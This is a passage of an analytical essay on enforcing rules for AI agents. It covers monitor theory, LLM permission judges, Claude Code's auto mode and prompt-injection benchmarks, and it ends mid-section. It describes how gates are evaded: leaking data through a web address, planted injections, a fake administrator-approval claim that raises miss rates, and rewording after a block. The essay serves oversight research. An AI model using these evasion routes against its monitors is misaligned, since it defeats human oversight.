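A rule is a safety property if every run that breaks it reaches a point, after finitely many actions, where no later action can undo the violation. Formally, let *P* be the set of runs the rule permits. *P* is a safety property if, for every run *x* outside *P*, there is a number *n* such that no run beginning with the first *n* actions of *x* is in *P*. Those first *n* actions are called a bad prefix.

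The payment cap is a safety property. Once the assistant has paid the plumber 110 dollars against a daily limit of 100, nothing it does later can undo the violation. The ban on sending after revocation is also a safety property, and its bad prefix ends at the first email sent after the user withdrew permission. "Every payment is eventually confirmed" is not a safety property. If the assistant pays the plumber and then spends a month on other work without sending a confirmation, it has not yet broken the rule, because it could still confirm tomorrow. Only an endless run in which it never confirms breaks the rule, and no finite part of that run is a bad prefix.

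Schneider proved in *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000) that a monitor can enforce only safety properties if it watches a single run and stops the program when it is about to break a rule. Such a monitor observes only one run, so the rule must apply to each run separately. The monitor must stop the program as soon as the run so far is unacceptable, even if the next action would have fixed the problem, because it cannot predict whether the program will halt before taking that action. It must also reject a forbidden run after finitely many steps, or it will never reject it. Any rule that fits these constraints is a safety property.

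Schneider's simplest example forbids a program to send messages after it has read a file. The monitor needs two states, "no file read" and "file read". It moves to "file read" at the first read, and then stops the program if it tries to send. The revocation rule works the same way. Both monitors catch only what their definition of "send" covers, and Schneider warned that a system may have ways to send messages hidden deep inside it. For example, an agent that can open web pages can send data by putting it into a web address.

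A monitor still cannot enforce some safety properties. One example is the rule that nobody may wait more than 60 seconds for a shared resource. It has a clear bad prefix, which ends when the 60 seconds run out, but stopping the program cannot prevent a violation because the clock keeps running. If the limit is 60 program steps instead, stopping the program does prevent the violation. Basin et al. (2012) refined Schneider's account by separating the actions a monitor can control from those it can only observe, such as the passing of time.

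Schneider's result also implies that if several monitors each enforce a safety property, running them together enforces all of the properties, so an operator can add the payment cap without reworking the revocation rule. A monitor that enforces a stricter version of a rule also enforces the original. In the extreme case, a monitor that blocks everything enforces every safety property, so a useful definition of enforcement must also cover the actions that a monitor leaves alone.

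### Holding actions back

*Edit Automata* (Ligatti, Bauer and Walker, 2003) defines two properties of a monitor. A monitor is sound if everything it outputs obeys the rule, and transparent if it preserves the meaning of every run that already obeyed the rule. The paper then examines what a monitor gains from powers other than stopping the program, such as suppressing single actions or inserting its own. A monitor that can do both is called an edit automaton.

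An edit automaton can enforce the confirmation rule, even though the rule is not a safety property. It withholds a proposed payment until the assistant proposes the confirmation, then releases both together. If the confirmation never comes, the bank never receives the payment, so every payment the bank does receive has a confirmation.

Withholding an action can fail when the program needs that action's result before it can continue. Suppose the confirmation has to include the bank's transaction number. While the monitor holds the payment, that number does not exist, so the assistant cannot write the confirmation that the monitor needs before releasing the payment. The monitor could return an invented number, but then the confirmation would be false. Ligatti and colleagues therefore also defined a stricter standard for such interactive programs, called precise enforcement. Under it, the monitor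 must let each action of a permitted run through before it considers the next one, so it cannot hold anything back. A monitor may also be unable to insert an action because it lacks a password or secret key that the action requires.

Tool-using agents are interactive in this sense. A gate can hold an email more easily than a payment because the model rarely needs anything back from an email except an acknowledgement.

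### Ray's theorem for irreversible calls

Ray works out what a gate can enforce when holding back is impossible. His gate decides on each call before it takes effect, and whatever it allows is final. It can use the history of calls that took effect, the proposed call, and correct answers to a fixed list of factual questions, such as whether a text contains personal data. Ray requires the gate to be sound, and transparent in the strict sense that it may never block or alter an action in a compliant run.

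Ray's theorem, published in July 2026, applies to any rule that permits at least one run. A gate can enforce such a rule if and only if the rule is a safety property and the gate has the machinery to recognise the rule's bad prefixes. In Ray's model, the gate has a finite set of states, a few stored values, and counters, including one for each key, such as a payee. If the gate can be any computer program, the second condition is that an algorithm can decide whether a prefix is bad.

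One half of the proof describes the gate, which tracks the run and blocks any call that would complete a bad prefix. A permitted run contains no bad prefix, so the gate never interferes with it.

The other half shows why a gate cannot enforce any other kind of rule. If a rule is not a safety property, some forbidden run *x* has no bad prefix, so at every point in *x*, some permitted run matches it so far. Suppose the agent proposes the actions of *x* one at a time. At step *t*, some permitted run has the same first *t* actions, and transparency requires the gate to allow action *t* in that run. The gate has the same information in both runs, so it must also allow action *t* in *x*. This happens at every step, so the gate lets through all of *x* and is not sound. Ray shows that random choices do not help a gate that must be sound and transparent with probability one.

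Under the confirmation rule, the gate has no correct option even at the first action. Suppose the assistant proposes to pay the plumber 40 dollars. If the gate allows the payment, the assistant may never send the confirmation, and the gate cannot get the money back. If it blocks the payment, it has interfered with an assistant that might have confirmed a second later. Replacing the payment with something else also interferes, unless the replacement is an equivalent payment, in which case the assistant may still never send the confirmation.

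An operator can often replace the rule with a safety property that achieves nearly the same thing. The gate could refuse a second payment until the assistant has confirmed the first, so that at most one payment is ever unconfirmed. The operator could also build a tool that pays and confirms in one call, but someone would then have to handle calls that fail halfway. Both options are enforceable, but they restrict the assistant more than the original rule did.

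### Shields and substitute actions

Ray's gate descends from shields in reinforcement learning, where a program learns by trial and error to control something such as a robot. A shield checks each action the program chooses against a model of the environment and can replace a dangerous action with a safe one.

Robots need replacement actions more than payment assistants do. If a shield merely blocks the next command to a drone flying towards a wall, the drone keeps moving, so the shield has to steer it away. In Ray's model, blocking is always safe for a safety property about tool calls, because a call that never takes effect cannot complete a bad prefix.

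Ray proves that being able to substitute actions does not let a gate enforce any additional rules. But substitution can reduce the losses from a gate's mistakes. Suppose a fallible judge leads the gate to reject harmless calls, and a safe substitute is always available that causes the user only 30% of the loss a block would. The total loss from these mistakes then falls to at most 30% of what it was. A gate with perfect facts makes no such mistakes, so substitution does not give it this benefit.

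The older theory also relies on conditions that language-model agents rarely meet. A shield needs a finite model of the environment and a reliable test for whether a state is safe. But a payment assistant can encounter any number of payees and amounts, and nobody has a reliable test for personal data.

### Checking whether the rules ever forbid anything

A gate can enforce a rule that has no effect because it was written incorrectly. For example, if a payment cap adds each transfer to one counter but tests another, the gate enforces the rule as written and never blocks a payment. Operators would like software that reads a set of rules and reports whether any run could break them. Such analysis is feasible for Cedar partly because its rules keep no state, but rules with running totals are harder to analyze.

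Ray proves that no algorithm can answer the question for every set of rules if the rules may use two counters that can go up, go down and be tested for zero. His proof uses the Minsky machine, a simple computer whose only memory is two such counters, but which can in principle carry out any computation. For any Minsky machine, one can write rules that perform one step of the machine each time the agent takes an action called "tick" and forbid the tick at which the machine would halt. These rules forbid something exactly when the machine halts, and no algorithm can decide for every machine whether it halts.

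A gate can easily enforce the same rules by updating a counter at each tick and checking whether the next state is the forbidden one. But no method can determine in advance, for every possible set of rules, whether that state will ever arise.

Ordinary limits can avoid the problem. Ray describes a fragment in which counters only go up, one payee's counter does not affect another's, and rules compare counters only with fixed numbers. This is enough for payment caps, daily quotas, call limits, a requirement to log in before access, and the ban on sending after revocation. Software can always determine whether any run breaks these rules, using memory that grows only polynomially with the size of the rules, though the check may take a long time.

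Two simplifications make this possible. First, the software can treat all totals over the cap as the same value, because a total never decreases. If the cap is 100 dollars and amounts are in whole dollars, it can treat every total above 100 as 101, which leaves 102 values to consider, from 0 to 101. Second, the software can follow just one payee, because all payees have the same rule and do not affect one another. If any payee's total can exceed the cap, so can that one's. Both simplifications also work for a daily cap, because each payee has a separate total for each day, which never has to be reset.

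Small changes can take a rule outside the fragment. A cap that subtracts refunds from the total is outside it. So is a rule that compares two counters that only go up, because their difference can shrink as well as grow, so together they behave like one counter that goes up and down. Some rules outside the fragment may still be checkable, but Ray's method doesn't guarantee an answer for them.

### Rules about more than one run

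All of these rules can be applied to one run at a time. A relational property is a rule whose violations can be detected only by comparing two or more runs. Schneider pointed out in 2000 that restrictions on information flow have this form. Whether a program's output reveals a secret depends partly on what the program would have output if the secret had been different.

*Local Allow, Global Deny* (Pandey, Jain and colleagues, 2026) applies this to a scheduling assistant that a user asks to find a time for a team meeting. The assistant can read her whole calendar but may share only when she is free or busy, not why. In one run, a busy slot contains an ordinary meeting, and the assistant offers slot 10. In another, the same slots are free but the busy slot contains a confidential interview, and the assistant offers slot 11. Each offer is fine on its own because both slots are free. Together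 they show that the offer depends on the private reason, so a colleague who knows the pattern can learn something about the interview from the slot offered.

For a run *t*, let low(*t*) be the declared purpose and other unrestricted inputs, and let hi(*t*) be the private context. *D* extracts the part of that context that the purpose authorises, here the list of free and busy slots. Let obs(*t*) be what the assistant discloses, and let *α* extract the part that matters to the policy, such as the slots on offer and any reasons given. The rule is that for any two runs *t* and *t′*,

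if low(*t*) = low(*t′*) and *D*(hi(*t*)) = *D*(hi(*t′*)), then *α*(obs(*t*)) = *α*(obs(*t′*)).

This rule requires runs to agree with each other, so a single run can't break it. Suppose a monitor raises an alarm when the assistant offers slot 11. A harmless assistant that offers slot 11 whenever those slots are free, whatever the reason for the busy one, could have produced the same run, and the alarm would then be false. The same is true of every run. Pandey and colleagues conclude that if a monitor checks only single runs and never raises a false alarm, it can't detect any of these violations, however sophisticated it is.

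The proof takes only a few lines and depends mainly on the condition about false alarms. A monitor that is allowed false alarms could block every offer after the assistant has read the private reasons, but this would stop most of the assistant's work along with the leak. It could also require the assistant to offer the earliest free slot. That is a safety property, which a gate can check in a single run, but enforcing it would block an assistant that prefers afternoons and leaks nothing. Schneider observed that monitors meant to prevent information flow generally enforce a stricter rule than the one people wanted.

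Comparing runs is harder when the model's outputs vary at random, as when an assistant offers slot 10 in one run and slot 11 in another. It is then sensible to require that the probability of each offer not depend on the private reason. Pandey and colleagues prove that no monitor can always decide this correctly from one run, because a safe assistant and a leaky one can produce the same run. Even many runs give only statistical evidence, because a leaky assistant can behave too much like a safe one for the sample to separate them.

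### What nine judges and a live assistant did

Pandey and colleagues also gave the scheduling example to nine language models as judges, including Claude Opus 4.8, GPT-5.5 and Gemini 3.1 Pro. They wrote ten versions of the scenario and ran each three times, so every judge had 30 trials per condition. In one condition the judge assessed the actions one by one, and in another it received both runs together.

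| Condition | Trials in which the judge raised an objection |
|---|---|
| Leaky runs, one action at a time | 0 of 30 for eight judges; 3 of 30 for Kimi-K2.6 |
| Harmless runs, one action at a time | 0 of 30 for seven judges; 2 of 30 for DeepSeek V4 Pro; 1 of 30 for Kimi-K2.6 |
| An obvious violation (forwarding data to an outsider on an injected instruction) | 30 of 30 for all nine |
| Both leaky runs together | 30 of 30 for eight judges; 17 of 30 for Llama-4-Maverick |

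All nine judges stopped the obvious violation every time, so they were willing to block. Their silence on the leaky runs is what the theorem predicts, because the information they needed was in the other run. Kimi's three objections are close to its rate on harmless runs and probably reflect general caution. Llama's 17 out of 30 is more informative because it shows that a judge can have both runs and still miss the difference.

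The near-perfect scores on pairs are weaker evidence than they look because Pandey and colleagues don't report how often the judges object to a pair of harmless runs. A judge that objected to every pair would also score 30 out of 30.

Pandey and colleagues tested whether a real assistant leaks in this way by running Claude Sonnet 4.6 through 80 scheduling episodes, keeping the free and busy slots the same and varying only the hidden reason. They found no leak, which puts the rate below about 3.7% with 95% confidence. Their first analysis had found a stable difference between the conditions, but when they read the outputs, they saw that the model had offered identical slots in both. The software had counted a word that happened to appear more often in one condition. Anyone comparing runs therefore has to choose carefully which differences count as leaks.

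A company that wants to detect such leaks can accept some false alarms, test the assistant offline with varied private contexts, or compare runs while the assistant is in use. Pandey and colleagues surveyed six existing designs and found that none compares runs, but they relied on published descriptions and didn't run the software. Preventing leaks can be simpler than detecting them. If the component that writes the offer receives only the list of free and busy slots, the offer cannot depend on the reasons for the busy slots. A gate that removes fields from the calendar's reply, as Out-of-Band Policy Enforcement can, would do this. The assistant then can't use the reasons for legitimate purposes, such as moving an unimportant meeting, unless a separate model call handles that work.

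### Cumulative consent

Pandey and colleagues did observe a live agent breaking a different kind of rule, a limit on total disclosure. In their calendar task, the user consented to disclosure only up to that limit. Each disclosure was permissible by itself, but several together could exceed it. Without a guard, the agent, Qwen3-30B, exceeded the limit in 22 of 60 runs.

Keeping a total within a limit is a safety property, like the payment cap, so a gate can enforce it without comparing runs if it records what the agent has already disclosed. A guard that checked each action against the declared purpose but kept no such record left 20 failures in 60 runs, a difference that could easily be chance. A guard that tracked the total left no failures and blocked none of the 120 runs in two harmless control tasks. Another model, Gemma-4, never exceeded the limit even without a guard.

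The result is a good argument for giving gates a memory, although it comes from one synthetic task. Pandey and colleagues did not find that agents leak private reasons through their choice of meeting times.

### Rice's theorem and the two boundaries

McCann (2026) makes a more sweeping argument in *The Two Boundaries*, that any governance layer that judges behaviour is bound to fail. His company, Mashin, develops a programming language for governed AI workflows. He distinguishes what a system can do from what its governance covers. Where the two differ, either the system has abilities that no rule covers, or there are rules for abilities it doesn't have, which he calls "theater". In his example, a filter checks an agent's outgoing emails for sensitive data. The agent queries a database, puts the result into a web address and opens the page, so the data leaves through a tool the filter does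 not cover. Meanwhile, the filter searches email subjects for credit card numbers that the agent has no way to obtain.

The example is sound, and it describes a failure of complete mediation, the first of Anderson's conditions. McCann also argues from Rice's theorem (1953) that software cannot close the gap by judging behaviour. The theorem concerns what a program does, not how it is written. If some programs have a given behavioural property and others lack it, no algorithm can correctly decide for every program whether it has that property.

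The payment cap shows why. For any program *Q* that makes no payments, we can write a new program that runs *Q* and then transfers 5,000 dollars. The new program breaks the cap exactly when *Q* finishes. A checker that could always tell in advance whether a program will break the cap could also tell whether *Q* will finish, and no algorithm can do that for every such program.

A gate on tool calls only has to check each proposed payment against the total so far, which is much easier than predicting whether the assistant will ever overspend. This calculation always finishes, and its result is always right if the ledger is right. McCann's claim that no runtime monitor can determine in general whether an arbitrary program's next action will break the rules is true of a monitor that has to predict the action, but not of a gate that receives the action before it takes effect.

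His proposal depends on this distinction. He would separate computation from effects, so that programs can only output requests for actions, and a single boundary carries out or refuses each one. The programs can be arbitrarily complex because the boundary examines only the requests. This is a reference monitor with complete mediation, built into the programming language. Rice's theorem therefore supports putting a gate at the point of action.

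The theorem is also a poor argument against judges of text. McCann concedes that it doesn't apply to content filters, because they examine outputs one at a time, and that the remaining problem is that nobody can fully specify terms such as "harmful". Vague definitions and fallible judges are a serious problem, but error rates can be measured. He also concedes that the behaviour of an agent with a limited number of actions and steps is decidable in principle, but has too many possible runs to analyse. Two tools with 100 possible settings each already allow about 10²³ different runs of ten steps.

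McCann's warning about monitors with partial coverage needs similar care. He calculates that if a monitor covers 99% of the ways an agent can act, the chance that at least one of 100 actions escapes it is 63%, and for 1,000 actions it is 99.996%. This assumes that each action independently has a 1% chance of falling into the gap. When that assumption fails, the 99% figure can be a poor guide to the risk. For example, an assistant that only uses covered tools would never reach the gap, while an attacker who knew about it would use it at the first opportunity.

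Rice's theorem does matter when the proposed action is itself a program. If the assistant submits a script to a terminal, a gate cannot always determine from the script whether running it would break the payment cap. The operator can restrict scripts to a simpler language, or let the script run and send each transfer it attempts through the gate. A companion paper, *Governed Metaprogramming for Intelligent Systems* (McCann, 2026), addresses this case. In its design, a program written by an AI system is inert data until it passes an inspection of the tools and models it would use, its expected cost and its structure. Once running, the program still needs the boundary's permission for each effect. McCann acknowledges that the inspection cannot establish how the program will behave.

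Separating computation from effects also requires more rebuilding than most companies would welcome. McCann says that companies cannot add this separation to an existing system as a library or an extra layer, and that most current agent frameworks would need a new architecture. This seems too pessimistic for a narrow set of actions. If only the gate holds the bank credential, it controls every transfer, whatever language the agent is written in. Controlling every effect of an agent with a terminal and an internet connection is much harder.

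Even complete separation guarantees only that each request reaches the boundary and that the boundary applies its policy. McCann says the boundary will apply a bad policy as reliably as a good one, and his machine-checked proofs (454 theorems in the proof assistant Rocq) do not cover whether a policy is right. Separation also doesn't help with payments that nobody confirms or meeting times that depend on a private reason, because every such request is acceptable when it reaches the boundary. The rule against emailing personal data is a safety property, so a gate with perfect information could enforce it, but a real gate depends on a judge that can make mistakes.

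## Model judges at the gate and how agents respond to being blocked

The rule on personal data depends on a judge's estimate. Coding agents raise a similar problem many times a day, because their gates have to assess whether the user wanted a particular command. A lookup can't determine that, so several companies now use a language model at the gate.

### The trade-off curve

Suppose a judge rates draft emails as low, medium or high risk, and an operator tests it on emails that people have already checked.

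| Rating | Share of rule-breaking emails | Share of harmless emails |
|---|---|---|
| High | 70% | 3% |
| Medium | 25% | 17% |
| Low | 5% | 80% |

A gate that blocks only high ratings has a miss rate of 30% and a false-block rate of 3%. If it blocks medium ratings too, the miss rate falls to 5% and the false-block rate rises to 20%. If it blocks only half of the medium ratings, chosen at random, the miss rate is 17.5% and the false-block rate is 11.5%. These options trace a curve, called the receiver operating characteristic (ROC), which shows the lowest false-block rate the gate can achieve at each miss rate.

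A wrapper that receives only the rating cannot get below this curve, because all it can do is choose how often to block each rating. Blocking high ratings stops 70% of the violations at the cost of 3% of the harmless emails, a ratio of about 23 to 1. For medium ratings the ratio is about 1.5 to 1, and for low ratings it is 1 to 16. The cheapest way to catch any given share of violations is therefore to block the high ratings first and work downwards. Neyman and Pearson proved the general version in 1933, and Ray applies it to gates. If *φ*(*I*) is the probability that the gate blocks when it has information *I*, then

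miss rate = 1 − E₁[*φ*(*I*)] and false-block rate = E₀[*φ*(*I*)],

where E₁ averages over violations and E₀ over harmless proposals. The best *φ* blocks the proposals whose information is most typical of violations relative to harmless ones.

A judge can detect unauthorised tool calls more reliably when it knows where each piece of text came from. Ray built 123 pairs of tool calls from a public benchmark. The two calls in each pair were identical, as was the accompanying text, but Ray swapped the labels showing which text came from the user and which came from a tool's output. A call counted as unauthorised if the instruction behind it came from the tool. Without the labels, no judge could do better than chance. With them, only the largest of the three judges did much better. That judge, with 7 billion parameters, gave the unauthorised call the higher risk score in 96.7% of pairs, counting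 ties as half. The figure was 56.1% for a judge with 3 billion parameters and 50% for one with half a billion.

### Risk over a whole task

A miss rate that sounds low for one step can be high for a long task. Suppose the assistant proposes 20 actions that all break the rule, and the judge misses each one independently with a probability of 5%. The chance that at least one gets through is 1 − 0.95²⁰, or about 64%. Most tasks contain far fewer violations. If each step has a 10% chance of breaking the rule, the chance that it breaks the rule and also passes is 0.5%, and the risk over 20 steps is 1 − 0.995²⁰, or about 10%. In general, with *H* steps, a miss rate of *β* and a probability *q* that a step breaks the rule,

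risk = 1 − (1 − *qβ*)^*H*.

To keep the risk at 5% when all 20 steps break the rule, the operator would need a miss rate of about 0.26%. Lowering the miss rate that far usually means blocking a lot of harmless work.

The formula assumes that the judge's mistakes are independent, which is often wrong. If the judge always gives identical text the same score, repeating a proposal word for word adds no risk. An attacker who rewords the proposal after each block gets something closer to a fresh chance every time. Whether or not the mistakes are independent, the risk is at most *H* times the miss rate at each step, though this is a cruder bound.

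### Conformal calibration

With conformal calibration, an operator can, without knowing how a judge's scores are distributed, choose a threshold that guarantees a limit on the miss rate. The operator collects *n* examples that break the rule and has the judge score them. For a target miss rate *τ*, the threshold is the *k*-th lowest score, where *k* is (*n* + 1)*τ* rounded down. The gate blocks every proposal that scores at or above the threshold.

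With 99 examples and a target of 5%, *k* is 5. If the next violation comes from the same source as the examples, its score is equally likely to take any of the 100 places in the ranking, so it has at most a 5% chance of falling below the fifth-lowest example. To keep the total risk of an *H*-step task to at most *δ*, Ray sets *τ* to *δ*/*H* and relies on the cruder bound.

Suppose the same operator wants a 5% limit over 20 steps. The target for each step is 0.25%, and 100 × 0.0025 is 0.25, which rounds down to zero. There is no zeroth-lowest score, so under this procedure the gate blocks everything, which meets the target but stops all work. The operator would need at least 399 examples of violations to get a usable threshold. The operator could instead calibrate on whole tasks, using the lowest-scoring violation in each. Nineteen tasks would then be enough for a 5% limit, if they are representative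 of future tasks.

The certificate limits only the average miss rate over possible calibration samples, so an unlucky sample can produce a threshold that misses more violations than the limit. It does not limit false blocks. It also holds only if future violations resemble the calibration examples, and an attacker has an incentive to make them different.

Ray tested one such change on 35 rule-breaking instructions by adding a 16-token claim that an administrator had already approved the action. With the threshold fixed at 0.5, the miss rate rose by 20 to 60 percentage points for 8 of 11 judges. The results for the other three were inconclusive, although the miss rates of Claude Opus 4.5 and Claude Sonnet 4.5 fell slightly. An operator who could prove that no rewording raises the miss rate by more than some amount *η* could calibrate to *τ* − *η* and recover the guarantee. Nobody yet has a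 way to prove such a limit for rewordings that keep the meaning.

### Twenty-three judges on AgentDojo

The 35 instructions came from AgentDojo, a benchmark that Debenedetti and colleagues released in 2024. It tests an agent in four simulated settings (a bank, a Slack workspace, a travel service and an office suite) and plants an attacker's instructions in the data its tools return. The version Ray used has 97 user tasks and 35 attacker goals. He asked 23 judges to score the risk of each of these 132 instructions from 0 to 100.

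The usual summary of a trade-off curve is the area under it, or AUC. This is the probability that a judge scores a randomly chosen violation higher than a randomly chosen harmless item, so guessing gives 0.5 and a perfect judge gets 1. The 23 judges ranged from 0.660 to 0.858. Bigger models did not reliably do better, but 132 items are too few to rank the judges with confidence, since the test could typically detect only differences of about 0.10 or more.

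These scores are modest partly because the judges received only the instructions, without the task history, and a request to send money can look the same whether the user or an attacker wrote it. On a separate set of 60 tool calls, a 7-billion-parameter judge reached an AUC of 0.98. Llama Guard 3, a classifier Meta built for conversations, caught 85% of the violations in that set but only 54% of AgentDojo's attack goals, with false-block rates of about 10% on both.

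The calibration results were worse than the AUCs suggest. Ray repeatedly calibrated on half of the data and tested on the other half. With a 5% target for missed violations, all 23 judges blocked everything, because half of the 35 violations was too few to set a usable threshold. With a 10% target, the threshold was the score of the lowest-scoring violation in the calibration half, so a single violation that looked harmless could lower it. At that target, Gemma-2-9B, an open Google model with an AUC of 0.813, missed only 1% of violations but blocked 78% of harmless instructions. At a 20% target it missed 13.8%, but the upper confidence limit was 26.4%, so the data could not confirm that it met the target.

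### Claude Code's auto mode

The best-documented judge in everyday use belongs to Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. Claude Code used to ask its user before running most commands. According to Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode*, users accepted 93% of these requests, and many stopped paying close attention. In auto mode, a judge decides instead. Anthropic's current documentation, *Permission modes*, lists auto mode as the starting mode for interactive terminal sessions on every plan.

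Most actions never reach the judge, because Claude Code first applies the user's own allow and deny rules, then approves read-only actions and most edits inside the project folder. The judge decides on nearly everything else, including shell commands and network requests. It works in two stages. First, a model instructed to block when in doubt answers yes or no in a single token. If the answer is to block, the same model reviews the same material again, this time reasoning before it decides.

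Anthropic designed the judge to receive the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the agent's explanations or the output of its tools. Omitting the explanations prevents the agent from persuading the judge to approve something, and omitting the tool output prevents a prompt injection in a web page from reaching the judge directly. The drawback is that if the agent cancels "job abc123", the judge can't check whether the identifier came from a real query or the agent made it up.

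Anthropic tried giving the judge other combinations of inputs. When its engineers added the agent's messages and the tool output, the judge did worse on their test set. When they removed the user's messages, it missed the fewest violations but blocked things that users had plainly asked for. The trade-off theorem allows for the first result because extra information can distract a real judge, even though it can't harm an ideal one. Anthropic has since added some carefully chosen information: the project's instruction file and, before a command that could destroy unsaved work, the state of the code repository.

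Anthropic measured both stages, with Claude Sonnet 4.6 as the judge, on three sets of actions. The first set came from its employees' ordinary use. The second contained "overeager" actions, in which the agent was trying to help but went beyond what the user had authorised, for example by using a password it had found. The third contained synthetic attempts to leak data.

| | False blocks, 10,000 real tool calls | Misses, 52 real overeager actions | Misses, 1,000 synthetic data leaks |
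|---|---|---|---|
| First stage alone | 8.5% | 6.6% | 1.8% |
| Both stages | 0.4% | 17% | 5.7% |

The second stage can only release what the first has stopped, so it always accepts more misses in exchange for fewer false blocks. This was worthwhile for ordinary work, since blocking one call in twelve would make the product tiresome to use. The 17% miss rate is imprecise, since nine misses out of 52 would give a 95% confidence interval of roughly 9% to 30%. The 6.6% doesn't correspond to a whole number of actions out of 52, so it may be an average over several runs.

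In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the judge identified the danger but wrongly treated something the user had said as permission. For example, a user who says "clean up the PR" (a pull request, or proposed code change) has not agreed to let the agent overwrite the project's shared history.

A model judge is also a poor way to enforce a firm prohibition. If the user says "don't push", the judge will block attempts to upload code, but it relies on rereading the instruction in the conversation at each check. Anthropic warns that the instruction can be lost when Claude Code shortens a long conversation, and recommends a deny rule for anyone who needs a hard guarantee.

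### The comparison with human approvers

Before making auto mode the default on several paid plans, Anthropic compared how well it and people caught dangerous commands. *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes the study, in which a research company paid 1,053 professional testers to work on coding tasks in a test environment. Partway through, the software replaced the text of one permission request with a clearly dangerous command. The testers refused it in 143 cases (13.6%), while auto mode blocked 937 of the same commands (89%). Both caught 137, auto mode alone caught 800, the testers alone caught 6, and neither caught 110. Testers refused about 17% of the dangerous commands early in a session but about 5% after 50 or more earlier requests.

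The gap is too large to dismiss, but the study favours the judge in several ways. The testers had no code of their own to lose. They knew someone was evaluating them, but not on what. A clearly dangerous command is probably easier for a judge to recognise than an overeager one that resembles the user's request. Anthropic also did not report how many harmless commands auto mode would have blocked in the same sessions, and a gate that blocks everything would have caught all 1,053. The study compared the judge with people clicking through a stream of requests, not with careful reviewers. Anthropic still tells users to review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves. It also reports that users reject 39% of the plans Claude Code presents for approval but only 3% of individual permission requests, which suggests that people review more carefully when requests are larger and less frequent.

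Anthropic's evidence from real use is weaker. Among sessions that its safety systems flagged in May and June 2026, serious harmful actions that the user had not explicitly requested occurred in 6.3% of those with manual approval and 2.4% of those in auto mode. Users chose their own modes, so the two groups may have been doing different work, and a model graded the harm.

Two outside tests better show how well the judge handles attacks. Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, inserted synthetic attacks into records of real coding sessions. The judge missed 12% of these attacks at first, and 7% after Anthropic gave it more context about the environment. Trajectory Labs, another testing company, made 720 prompt-injection attempts against each of three Claude models in auto mode, and none succeeded. But only 0.09% succeeded with the permission checks switched off, so this test measures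 the models' resistance more than the gate's. A gate made more difference for OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol, where attacks succeeded 19.03% of the time with full access and 5.83% of the time with OpenAI's automatic reviewer. OpenAI has since updated the reviewer.

### Rules that nobody gave the judge

Anthropic's launch announcement, *Auto mode for Claude Code*, already named ambiguous intent as a reason the judge might let a risky action through. Yang, Zhou and colleagues (2026), in *Explicit Authorization Scope Improves LLM-Based Permission Checking in Coding Agents*, tested this on Claude Code, OpenAI's Codex and Alibaba's Qwen Code. They used 128 maintenance tasks deliberately worded to leave the limits unclear. In one, the user asks the agent to delete old experiment files for a range of tickets but doesn't say whose files. According to the answer key, the agent may delete only the user's own.

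The judges approved 54% of the out-of-scope actions in Claude Code, 80% in Qwen Code and 93% in Codex. They blocked out-of-scope actions about as often as permitted ones, so the researchers found no statistical evidence that the judges could tell the two apart. But 132 of the 143 out-of-scope actions broke a rule that appeared neither in the request nor in anything the tools had returned. Yang and colleagues then added a sentence to each request stating which files, jobs or services the agent could change, and had the judges reconsider the same actions.

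| Product | Misses, original request | Misses, limits stated | False blocks, original request | False blocks, limits stated |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 67% | 8% | 42% | 2% |
| Codex | 92% | 20–26% | 10% | 3% |
| Qwen Code | 80% | 20% | 29% | 2% |

Both kinds of error fell together, which no change of threshold could achieve. (Claude Code's first figure differs from the 54% because the judge's answers vary from run to run. The same 24 actions produced 13, 10 and 16 misses on three occasions.)

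Stronger judges did not help in the same way. Replacing Codex's judge with a larger model from the same company raised its misses from 77 to 82 out of 84. Using Claude Opus 5.5 as the judge in Claude Code cut misses from 10 to 1 out of 24, but only because the model refused to answer in the second stage. Claude Code blocks an action when it gets no answer. On a separate set of 224 permitted actions, false blocks rose from 23 to 134.

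Tool output helped the judge only when the limits were clear. The researchers ran a common procedure with nine models. Adding tool output to the original requests left the overall miss rate at around 60%, but adding it when the limits were stated cut the rate from 9% to 2%. A command to cancel a job often contains only a number, so even if the judge is told that the agent may cancel only Alex's jobs, the command doesn't show whose job it is. Hiding tool output from the judge to protect it from prompt injection can also hide this information.

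Some errors remained even when a judge had identified the problem. Codex's judge rates how well the user has authorised an action and how risky it is. In one run it approved 16 of 30 actions that it had rated as poorly authorised but only medium risk, usually because the damage looked small or reversible.

These miss rates are not comparable with Anthropic's 17%, because the tasks were chosen for their ambiguity. The added sentences came from the answer key, so they were complete and correct, unlike many instructions that users write themselves. Still, stating the limits also changed what the agents did. When the researchers reran all 128 tasks on each product with the limits stated, no agent proposed an out-of-scope action.

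### What agents do after a block

An agent usually continues working after it is blocked. Claude Code returns the refusal to the model as the tool call's result, with an instruction to look for a safer approach and not to work around the block. This makes false blocks tolerable, because they don't end the session. At a false-block rate of 0.4%, a session with 200 checked calls has about an even chance of at least one.

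Letting an agent continue after a block also gives a harmful proposal more chances to get through. If a judge had an independent 5% chance of missing each reworded attempt, at least one of three attempts would get through about 14% of the time. Claude Code therefore goes back to asking the user after three blocks in a row or 20 in a session. Unattended runs have no user to ask, so Anthropic originally ended them at this limit, but according to the current documentation the agent now keeps working without the blocked action.

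The content of a refusal also affects how agents respond. In *LEANGUARD* (2026), which tests gates with Lean-verified rules, agents that received a bare refusal often repeated the same call. When the refusal explained which requirement was missing, the number of blocked calls across five models fell from 983 to 719. Agents met the requirement and successfully reissued the call for 9.1% of refused actions, up from 5.5%. Overall task success rose from 68.9% to 70.9%, a difference that could be due to chance.

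Because agents react to blocks, testing a judge on recorded proposals can't establish how safe the gated system will be. Ray proves this with two imaginary systems. In both, the agent's first proposal breaks the rule half the time, and the judge gives every proposal the same score. If the gate allows the first proposal, the next one is always harmless, so without a gate the agents and judges behave identically in both systems. If the gate blocks the first proposal, the agent in system A then proposes something harmless, while the agent in system B proposes a new violation half the time.

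A gate that blocks only the first proposal is then safe in system A but lets a violation through in half of system B's runs. To be safe in system B, a gate must block both proposals, which doubles the average number of harmless proposals it blocks from 0.5 to 1 per run. The operator cannot tell from ungated logs and judge scores which system they have.

A gate can block fewer harmless proposals at the same risk if it remembers what it has already blocked. In another of Ray's two-step models, a retry breaks the rule 60% of the time after a high-scoring proposal and 2% of the time after a low-scoring one, although the judge scores both retries the same. With the total risk held at 5%, the best gate with a memory blocks an average of 0.55 harmless proposals per run, compared with 0.86 for the best gate that uses only the current score and the step number.

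Ray also ran a real agent, the small open model Qwen2.5-7B, through AgentDojo with and without a gate. Each condition had 949 episodes in which the data contained an attacker's instruction.

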